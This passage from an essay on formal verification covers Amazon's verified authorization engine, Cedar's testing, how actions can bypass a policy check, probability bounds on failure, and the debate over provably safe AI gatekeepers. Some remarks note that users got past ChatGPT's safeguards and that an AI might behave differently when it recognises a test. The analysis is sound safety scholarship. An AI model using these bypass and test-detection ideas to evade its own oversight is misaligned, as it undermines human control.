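Amazon took a similar approach with the engine that decides who may do what in its cloud services, which answers more than a billion requests per second. Chakarov, Geldenhuys and colleagues, in *Formally Verified Cloud-Scale Authorization*, describe how they replaced the old Java engine over four years. The Java code was too hard to verify directly, so they wrote a new engine in Dafny, proved that it meets a specification, and compiled it back to Java:

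| Part | Lines |
|---|---|
| Specification and proofs | 11,570 |
| Assumptions about Java's libraries | 1,557 |
| Engine in Dafny | 2,751 |
| Generated Java | 3,303 |

The trusted base still includes the library assumptions and the compiler. Chakarov's team built their own compiler, which produces Java that closely follows the Dafny source, so that engineers who don't know Dafny can review the result.

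They also needed evidence that the specification described the old engine, which customers relied on. During 2023 they ran both engines on real requests, starting with 0.1% of them and increasing to all. The engines sometimes disagreed because the specification had missed a subtlety of the old engine. After eight versions, the two engines agreed on 10^15 requests. The new engine went into service in 2024 and is three times as fast.

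### Testing the code against the model

Amazon chose a cheaper method for Cedar, the policy language that OpenShell is adopting for agents. A Cedar policy either permits or forbids certain actions. The engine allows a request if at least one permit applies and no forbid does. Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024), in *How We Built Cedar*, wrote a model of the engine in Lean and a separate, faster program in Rust. They proved theorems about the model, including these:

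- If any forbid applies, the engine denies the request.
- If no permit applies, the engine denies the request.
- The order of the policies doesn't affect the decision.
- Leaving out policies that the engine has identified as irrelevant doesn't affect it either.
- A policy that passes Cedar's validator never causes a type error.

The last theorem took most of the work. It matters because Cedar ignores any policy that causes an error. If a forbid policy refers to a file's "pwner" instead of its "owner", it forbids nothing, and the engine may allow the action, whereas LeanGuard would deny it. Cedar users therefore need the validator to find such mistakes in advance.

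The Lean model has 1,673 lines and its proofs have 5,714, compared with 15,693 lines of production code in Rust. Disselkoen's team decided against deploying the Lean version because few programmers know Lean and it lacks many useful libraries. They also judged that the tools for verifying Rust were not yet good enough. Instead, they use *differential testing*, which runs the model and the production code on the same random inputs and reports any disagreement. Where no model exists, they test properties of the Rust code directly. Each method found bugs:

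| Method | Part of Cedar | Bugs |
|---|---|---|
| Proofs about the Lean model | Validator | 4 |
| Comparing Rust with Lean | Decision engine | 6 |
| Comparing Rust with Lean | Validator | 4 |
| Testing properties of the Rust code | Reading policies | 6 |
| Testing properties of the Rust code | Formatting policies | 2 |
| Testing properties of the Rust code | Validator | 3 |

One of the bugs found through the proofs could make the validator run forever, and testing would probably have missed it. The code that reads policies has no Lean model, so neither a proof nor a comparison with a model could have found its six bugs. The tests for that code write out a random policy, read it back and check that nothing has changed.

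If a program generates a random policy, data and request independently, the policy will mostly refer to things that don't exist, and the tests will exercise little except the error messages. Cedar's generator therefore first invents a description of the data, then creates data, policies and requests that fit it.

The Java refund program shows what happens without such care. When the agent has already paid 60, only 60 of the 4.3 billion possible amounts make the Java version disagree with ACL2. A random amount has about a one in 72 million chance of exposing the error, so a million random tests would probably miss it. A generator that always tries the largest possible number would find it immediately. Cedar's tests have also increased in number, to about 100 million a night according to *Your Code Has Bugs. Lean4 Has Proofs* (Pant, 2026).

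Proofs now also cover tools that analyse Cedar policies. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) presents verified building blocks for translating policies into formulas for an SMT solver. Modelling five analyses with these blocks and proving them correct took one working day. The solver remains in the trusted base, so a bug in it could still hide a difference between two policies.

### Actions that bypass the check

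Cedar decides only the requests that an application sends to it. If a programmer forgets to make the application send a request before deleting a file, the application deletes the file, and every theorem about Cedar remains true. The proofs about LeanGuard and PocketFlow also assume that every action with consequences passes through the verified code.

For an agent, this assumption can fail in many places. The refund agent might have a general tool for running commands, with the payment service's password stored where those commands can read it. The shop could remove the tool, but a later developer might add another. It is safer to give the password only to the policy check and have the payment service reject any request without it. The shop then no longer has to trust every part of the agent's code, only the payment service's login and whatever keeps the agent away from the password.

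The payment service must also carry out the action the check approved. Fonseca's group found that a Verdi server could mistake part of a client's text for an additional command. If the payment service had this fault, it might read part of a customer's note as a second refund command and pay two refunds when the check had approved only one.

Isolation from the outside world is also an assumption, and it can be false from the start. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (September 2026) reports tests that were presented as simulations but were connected to the internet because of a misconfiguration.

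The shop can test its setup by going into the agent's environment and requesting a small refund without going through the check, which the payment service should refuse. This test covers only the routes that someone thinks to try, so the shop should also compare the payments on its bank statements with the approvals in the check's journal. A payment without an approval means that some route bypasses the check, but the comparison can show this only after the money has been paid.

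## What has to be measured, and how far proofs can support a claim of safety

Suppose the shop has proved that its agent never refunds more than 100 for a purchase, and its insurer asks how likely an overpayment is. The theorem doesn't give that probability, because it holds only under assumptions that may be false. The shop has to estimate how often each assumption fails.

### Adding up the ways to fail

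Let A1, …, An be assumptions that together make harm impossible. Harm can then happen only if at least one of them fails, so

P(harm) ≤ P(A1 fails) + P(A2 fails) + … + P(An fails)

The bound holds even if the assumptions don't fail independently. If one power cut corrupts the records and also disables the policy check, the sum counts that event twice, which can only make the bound too high.

The numbers in this example are invented:

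| Assumption | Failures per million purchases |
|---|---|
| The records include every earlier refund for the purchase | 1,000 |
| Every payment passes through the check | 10 |
| The running code makes the same decision as the ACL2 function | 1 |
| Sum | 1,011 |

The chance of an overpayment is therefore at most about 0.1% per purchase, or 1,000 in a million, and errors in the records account for 99% of that bound. Halving those errors would lower the bound by 500 in a million, while verifying the compiler could lower it by at most 1 in a million.

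The sum covers only the assumptions that someone has listed. For example, the assumption that nobody asks twice would not have been in the table until someone thought of splitting a refund.

### What a clean series of trials shows

To estimate the first number, the shop can pick purchases at random and compare the agent's records with the bank statements. If each comparison has the same probability p of revealing an error, independently of the others, the probability that n comparisons reveal none is (1 − p)^n. The usual 95% upper bound is the value of p for which this probability is 5%:

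(1 − p)^n = 0.05, which gives p ≈ 3/n

The 3 comes from −ln(0.05) ≈ 2.996. After 3,000 comparisons without an error, the bound is 0.1%, or 1,000 in a million. If the true rate were any higher, fewer than 5% of such samples would be free of errors. Lowering the bound to the second number in the table would take 300,000 error-free comparisons, and lowering it to the third would take 3 million.

One error among the 3,000 raises the bound to about 0.16%. The shop can't correct the cause and then count the other 2,999 as clean, because the correction may have introduced a worse fault. Littlewood and Strigini (1993), in *Validation of Ultra-High Dependability for Software-based Systems*, see no way to gain confidence in such a correction except to run the new version for a long time without a failure.

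Adding three 95% bounds also weakens the conclusion, since there is up to a 15% chance that at least one bound is too low. For 95% confidence in the sum, the shop can use 4.1/n for each assumption instead of 3/n.

Some results, such as LeanGuard's count of zero forbidden calls, follow from the system's design and need no such statistics. But how often LeanGuard's record of a customer's consent is wrong has to be measured.

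Unlike the other rows, the last row of the table is a yes-or-no property, whether the code matches the ACL2 function for every input. A proof that it does is evidence that there are no mismatches, which Littlewood and Strigini (2011), in *Validation of ultra-high dependability…*, call evidence for a "probability of perfection". Suppose the shop is 99% sure that the proof is right and applies to the running code, and 30,000 clean trials suggest that any remaining mismatch affects at most 1 request in 10,000. Multiplying 1% by 1 in 10,000 gives a chance of at most roughly 1 in a million that a mismatch affects a given request. Testing alone would have needed 3 million clean trials to support that figure.

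The 99% figure is the weak point. Littlewood and Strigini complained in 2011 that nobody was collecting data on how often a "proved" property turns out to be false. The later study by Fonseca's group provides only a small amount of this data.

### Why testing can't show very low failure rates

A commonly quoted requirement for airliners is fewer than one catastrophic failure per billion hours of flight. Even at that rate, Littlewood and Strigini point out, a fleet of 1,000 aircraft would have about a 10% chance of such a failure over 30 years. But by the 3/n rule, showing by testing that an airliner meets the requirement would take 3 billion hours without a failure, or about 340,000 years.

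Butler and Finelli (1993), in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software*, considered a system that may fail once in a billion ten-hour missions. One failure would take 1.14 million years on average to appear with one copy of the system, and 114 years with 10,000 copies running at once. Finding and removing bugs doesn't avoid the problem, because the frequent ones appear first. Littlewood and Strigini cite data on some large systems in which about a third of the faults each caused an error about once in 5,000 years of running.

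Testing is more practical for software that runs rarely and quickly. Butler and Finelli calculate that if a system receives one input a day and each test takes a tenth of a second, the million years of testing fall to 1.3 years. The function decide-total could process millions of artificial requests in a short time. Littlewood and Strigini accepted in 2011 that faster computers had made very long simulated tests feasible, but noted that the main doubt is then whether the test equipment and whatever judges the answers are correct. For the refund agent, the slow part is finding out what the shop has really paid.

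Redundancy adds less safety when components tend to fail on the same inputs. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) give the standard calculation in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*: two components that each fail once in n cases fail together only once in n², so one in a thousand becomes one in a million. They suggest that several AI models together might detect malicious inputs in this way. The calculation assumes independent failures, but experiments with programs written by separate teams found much less improvement than independence would give. Littlewood and Strigini explain that some inputs are harder than others, so when one program fails on an input, the other is more likely to fail on it too. Two language models trained on similar text would probably have the same problem.

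### Adversaries and changed conditions

The 3/n rule assumes that the trials are independent and resemble future use. If the shop generates its 3,000 trials from 30 templates, and all trials from the same template succeed or fail together, it effectively has 30 trials and a bound of about 10%.

An attacker who chooses the inputs breaks the rule more thoroughly. Random amounts would almost never trigger the overflow in the Java refund program, but a customer who knows about it can cause it every time. Dalrymple and colleagues note that OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months before release, yet users got around its safeguards within a day. A capable AI system might also recognize a test and behave differently during it, and the results would then reveal little about its later behaviour.

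Conditions can change without any attack. A self-driving car may have a good record because other drivers are cautious around it, and the record becomes less relevant once they get used to it and drive more aggressively.

A theorem about every input does not have this weakness, because it covers the inputs an attacker would choose. The attacker has to make an assumption fail instead, perhaps by finding a payment route that bypasses the check. The "10 in a million" for that assumption was at best a frequency among ordinary purchases, and it does not bound the chance that someone searching for such a route will succeed.

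### The proposal for guaranteed safe AI

Testing is least informative about rare failures and deliberate attacks, which are major concerns with very capable AI. Some researchers therefore want the case for safety to rest mainly on proofs. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) argue in *Provably safe systems* that proof is the only way to guarantee control of artificial general intelligence, meaning AI that can do practically any task as well as a human expert. In their design, AI systems write programs together with proofs that the programs meet human requirements. Computer chips run only programs whose proofs they have checked. Drones, DNA synthesizers and other dangerous machines also check a formal condition before they act.

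Tegmark and Omohundro's central argument is that no AI system, however intelligent, can prove a false theorem or do what is provably impossible, while checking a proof takes little computation. The claim about false theorems holds for a consistent logic but not for every program that checks proofs, as the OpenAI agent's two false proofs in Lean showed. Tegmark and Omohundro also expect that most of the deployed programs would not be neural networks, whose workings they consider too messy to verify. Neural networks would discover useful algorithms, and AI tools would turn these into ordinary code. It is unknown how much of a language model's ability could survive that conversion.

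Dalrymple and colleagues describe a broader family of approaches with three components. The proof about the braking car has all of them in miniature:

| Component | What it should deliver | Braking car |
|---|---|---|
| World model | A mathematical description of how the AI system's actions affect the world, including the uncertainty | The equations of motion |
| Safety specification | A precise statement of which effects are acceptable | The car never passes the obstacle |
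| Verifier | A proof or a probability bound, relative to the world model, that the system meets the specification | KeYmaera X and its proof |

The definition accepts a sound upper limit on the probability of harm in place of certainty, and society should ideally decide how much risk is acceptable. The world model can allow a person any behaviour from a wide set without predicting which will occur, as the crosswind model did with the wind. Safety must then be proved for every behaviour in the set.

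Dalrymple and colleagues anticipate the objection that the world is too complex to model. They answer in part that the guarantee can account for the model's own unreliability. If the world model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a system that is provably safe for n steps in the model is safe in reality with probability at least (1 − ε)^n. With one step per second and ε at one in a million, this bound falls to 92% after a day, 55% after a week and practically zero after a year.

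Their second answer is that an AI system able to carry out elaborate dangerous plans would show that sufficiently accurate world models are possible. This seems weaker, because an attacker needs a model that is accurate for one plan, while a guarantee requires one that covers every plan. Their third answer is that every approach to safety relies on beliefs about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit. That is a good reason to write the assumptions down, but writing them down doesn't make them more likely to be true.

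### Dickson's objections

Andrew Dickson's *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) argues that proofs apply to systems of symbols, and that models of the physical world and of people will be too incomplete for strong guarantees in the near term. One example is the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Engineers had used formal verification to rule out certain faults in the lander's software, but they had no proof about the landing itself. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and one analysis attributes about 20% of the risk to software. On those figures, perfect software would reduce the chance of failure only from 50% to about 40%.

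Dickson's main example is the DNA synthesizer. Tegmark and Omohundro wrote that such machines should not operate without a proof of safety, and that AI systems for biochemical design should produce only designs that are provably safe for humans. Dickson replies that predicting exactly what a new virus would do would require simulating it in a human body for years. In 2022 a leading simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of one unusually simple cell, while a human body has about 36 trillion cells. The starting data for such a simulation are also missing. A research project at Google took years to map a millionth of a human brain, and the map filled 1.4 petabytes.

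Misinformation is harder still, because a developer can't know who will read a chatbot's answer or where they will repeat it, and even a true statement can mislead people when quoted out of context. Finally, even if a proof about a machine is correct, the buyer would need repeated physical inspections to confirm that the machine they have is the one the proof describes.

The talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, by the maintainer of the widely used testing library Hypothesis, adds that a world model and a specification only move the problem, since someone still has to show that the model matches reality. The speaker would rather spend the effort asking directly what could go wrong. Young, in *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety*, goes further and argues that the limits are fundamental. Part of Young's case is that even simplified versions of the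 problem of a system verifying its own meaning are NP-complete, so no known method solves every case quickly. But solvers handle many practical cases of NP-complete problems, which makes this point less decisive than it sounds.

### Omohundro's reply

In the discussion below Dickson's essay, Omohundro agreed with most of the specific points but not with the conclusion. Omohundro wrote that engineers do not have to verify arbitrary systems because they can design new ones that are provably safe. The aim was to protect hardware, software and other infrastructure against attacks by AI systems, and the first goals did not include proofs about large neural networks.

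For DNA synthesis, Omohundro proposed a much narrower theorem. The machine would make only sequences with a digital signature from an authority that had judged them safe, and it would erase its secret keys if anyone tampered with it. The proof needs a model of the machine, including every way of tampering with it that the sensors must detect, but no model of the human body. Omohundro conceded that physical failures can't be prevented entirely, and wanted engineers to bound their probability and limit the damage.

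This proposal is better than the one Dickson attacked, but more modest than the most ambitious passages of the 2023 paper. Engineers could plausibly prove that a well-designed machine makes only signed sequences. To conclude that it makes nothing harmful, they would also have to assume that the authority never signs a dangerous sequence, and that assumption is now part of the sum.

The ACAS X proofs support both sides, since they establish a narrow physical claim but depend on assumptions about how pilots respond.

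### Where the proposal stands in 2026

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) is spending £59 million on a programme that Dalrymple started, the largest test of these ideas in the sources here. The original plan, which has since changed, was to show that AI can do valuable work under mathematical guarantees, and so build agreement that powerful AI should operate only behind a "gatekeeper" that verifies its outputs.

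Ammann's *Safeguarded AI*, the programme's revised plan of May 2026, reports that timely international agreement on such a gatekeeper has become less likely. The programme moved £18 million from training specialized AI models to building tools that let AI agents write and check proofs. A gatekeeper cannot protect people from a model that can be run without it, and according to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, rapid progress had also disproved the hypothesis that high-risk AI might not become openly available.

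The ARIA programme's first applications are now in cybersecurity. It is funding eight projects with £22 million, including work on containing AI agents and protecting the code on Android devices. In an earlier American military research programme, formally verified components such as the seL4 operating-system kernel withstood sustained attacks by testers on real systems, including a helicopter. Dalrymple is now the ARIA programme's technical adviser, Ammann directs it, and it ends in late 2027.

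The new plan takes up several of the critics' points. Ammann expects that as AI systems do more of the proving, trust will depend mainly on the specifications and assumptions, which people will have to examine carefully. The plan also lists as an open problem how an outsider can know that a proof applies to the system in question. Dickson had recommended continuing to verify the software of power plants and other infrastructure, so the two sides now largely agree on what to verify first. ARIA still has wider ambitions than Dickson, and hopes to extend the tools to energy grids, supply chains and medical devices.

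### Facts and the meaning of "guarantee"

Some of the remaining disagreements are about facts. One is whether AI will improve models of the world as quickly as it has improved proofs. Dickson expected AI to help much more with proving than with modelling and specification. The long proofs that agents now write, and the flawed specifications in benchmarks such as CLEVER, fit that expectation so far, though they concern software, not biology. Another question is whether companies and governments would accept hardware that refuses to run unproved programs. ARIA's experience with the gatekeeper is evidence that they would not accept it soon.

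Other disagreements come from the word "guarantee". Dickson takes it to mean that a system in the physical world will certainly not fail, a standard no engineered system meets. Tegmark and Omohundro invited this reading when they wrote of AI that provably never lies or escapes. Dalrymple and colleagues also count a probability bound that holds relative to a world model as a guarantee, which makes the proofs about the braking car and the refund agent small examples. Tegmark has used this weaker sense too, arguing in the talk *Provably Safe AI* that general AI without at least quantitative safety bounds should be illegal.

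Agreeing on the weaker meaning wouldn't end the dispute. Dickson fairly objects that even a 1% chance of producing a dangerous pathogen is too high to be interesting. A bound of one in a billion would be interesting, but it is hard to justify. For the DNA synthesizer, the bound depends on how often the authority signs a dangerous sequence. After 3,000 correct decisions, the authority could claim only an error rate below 0.1%, and only for requests like those it had already seen, not for sequences designed to deceive it.
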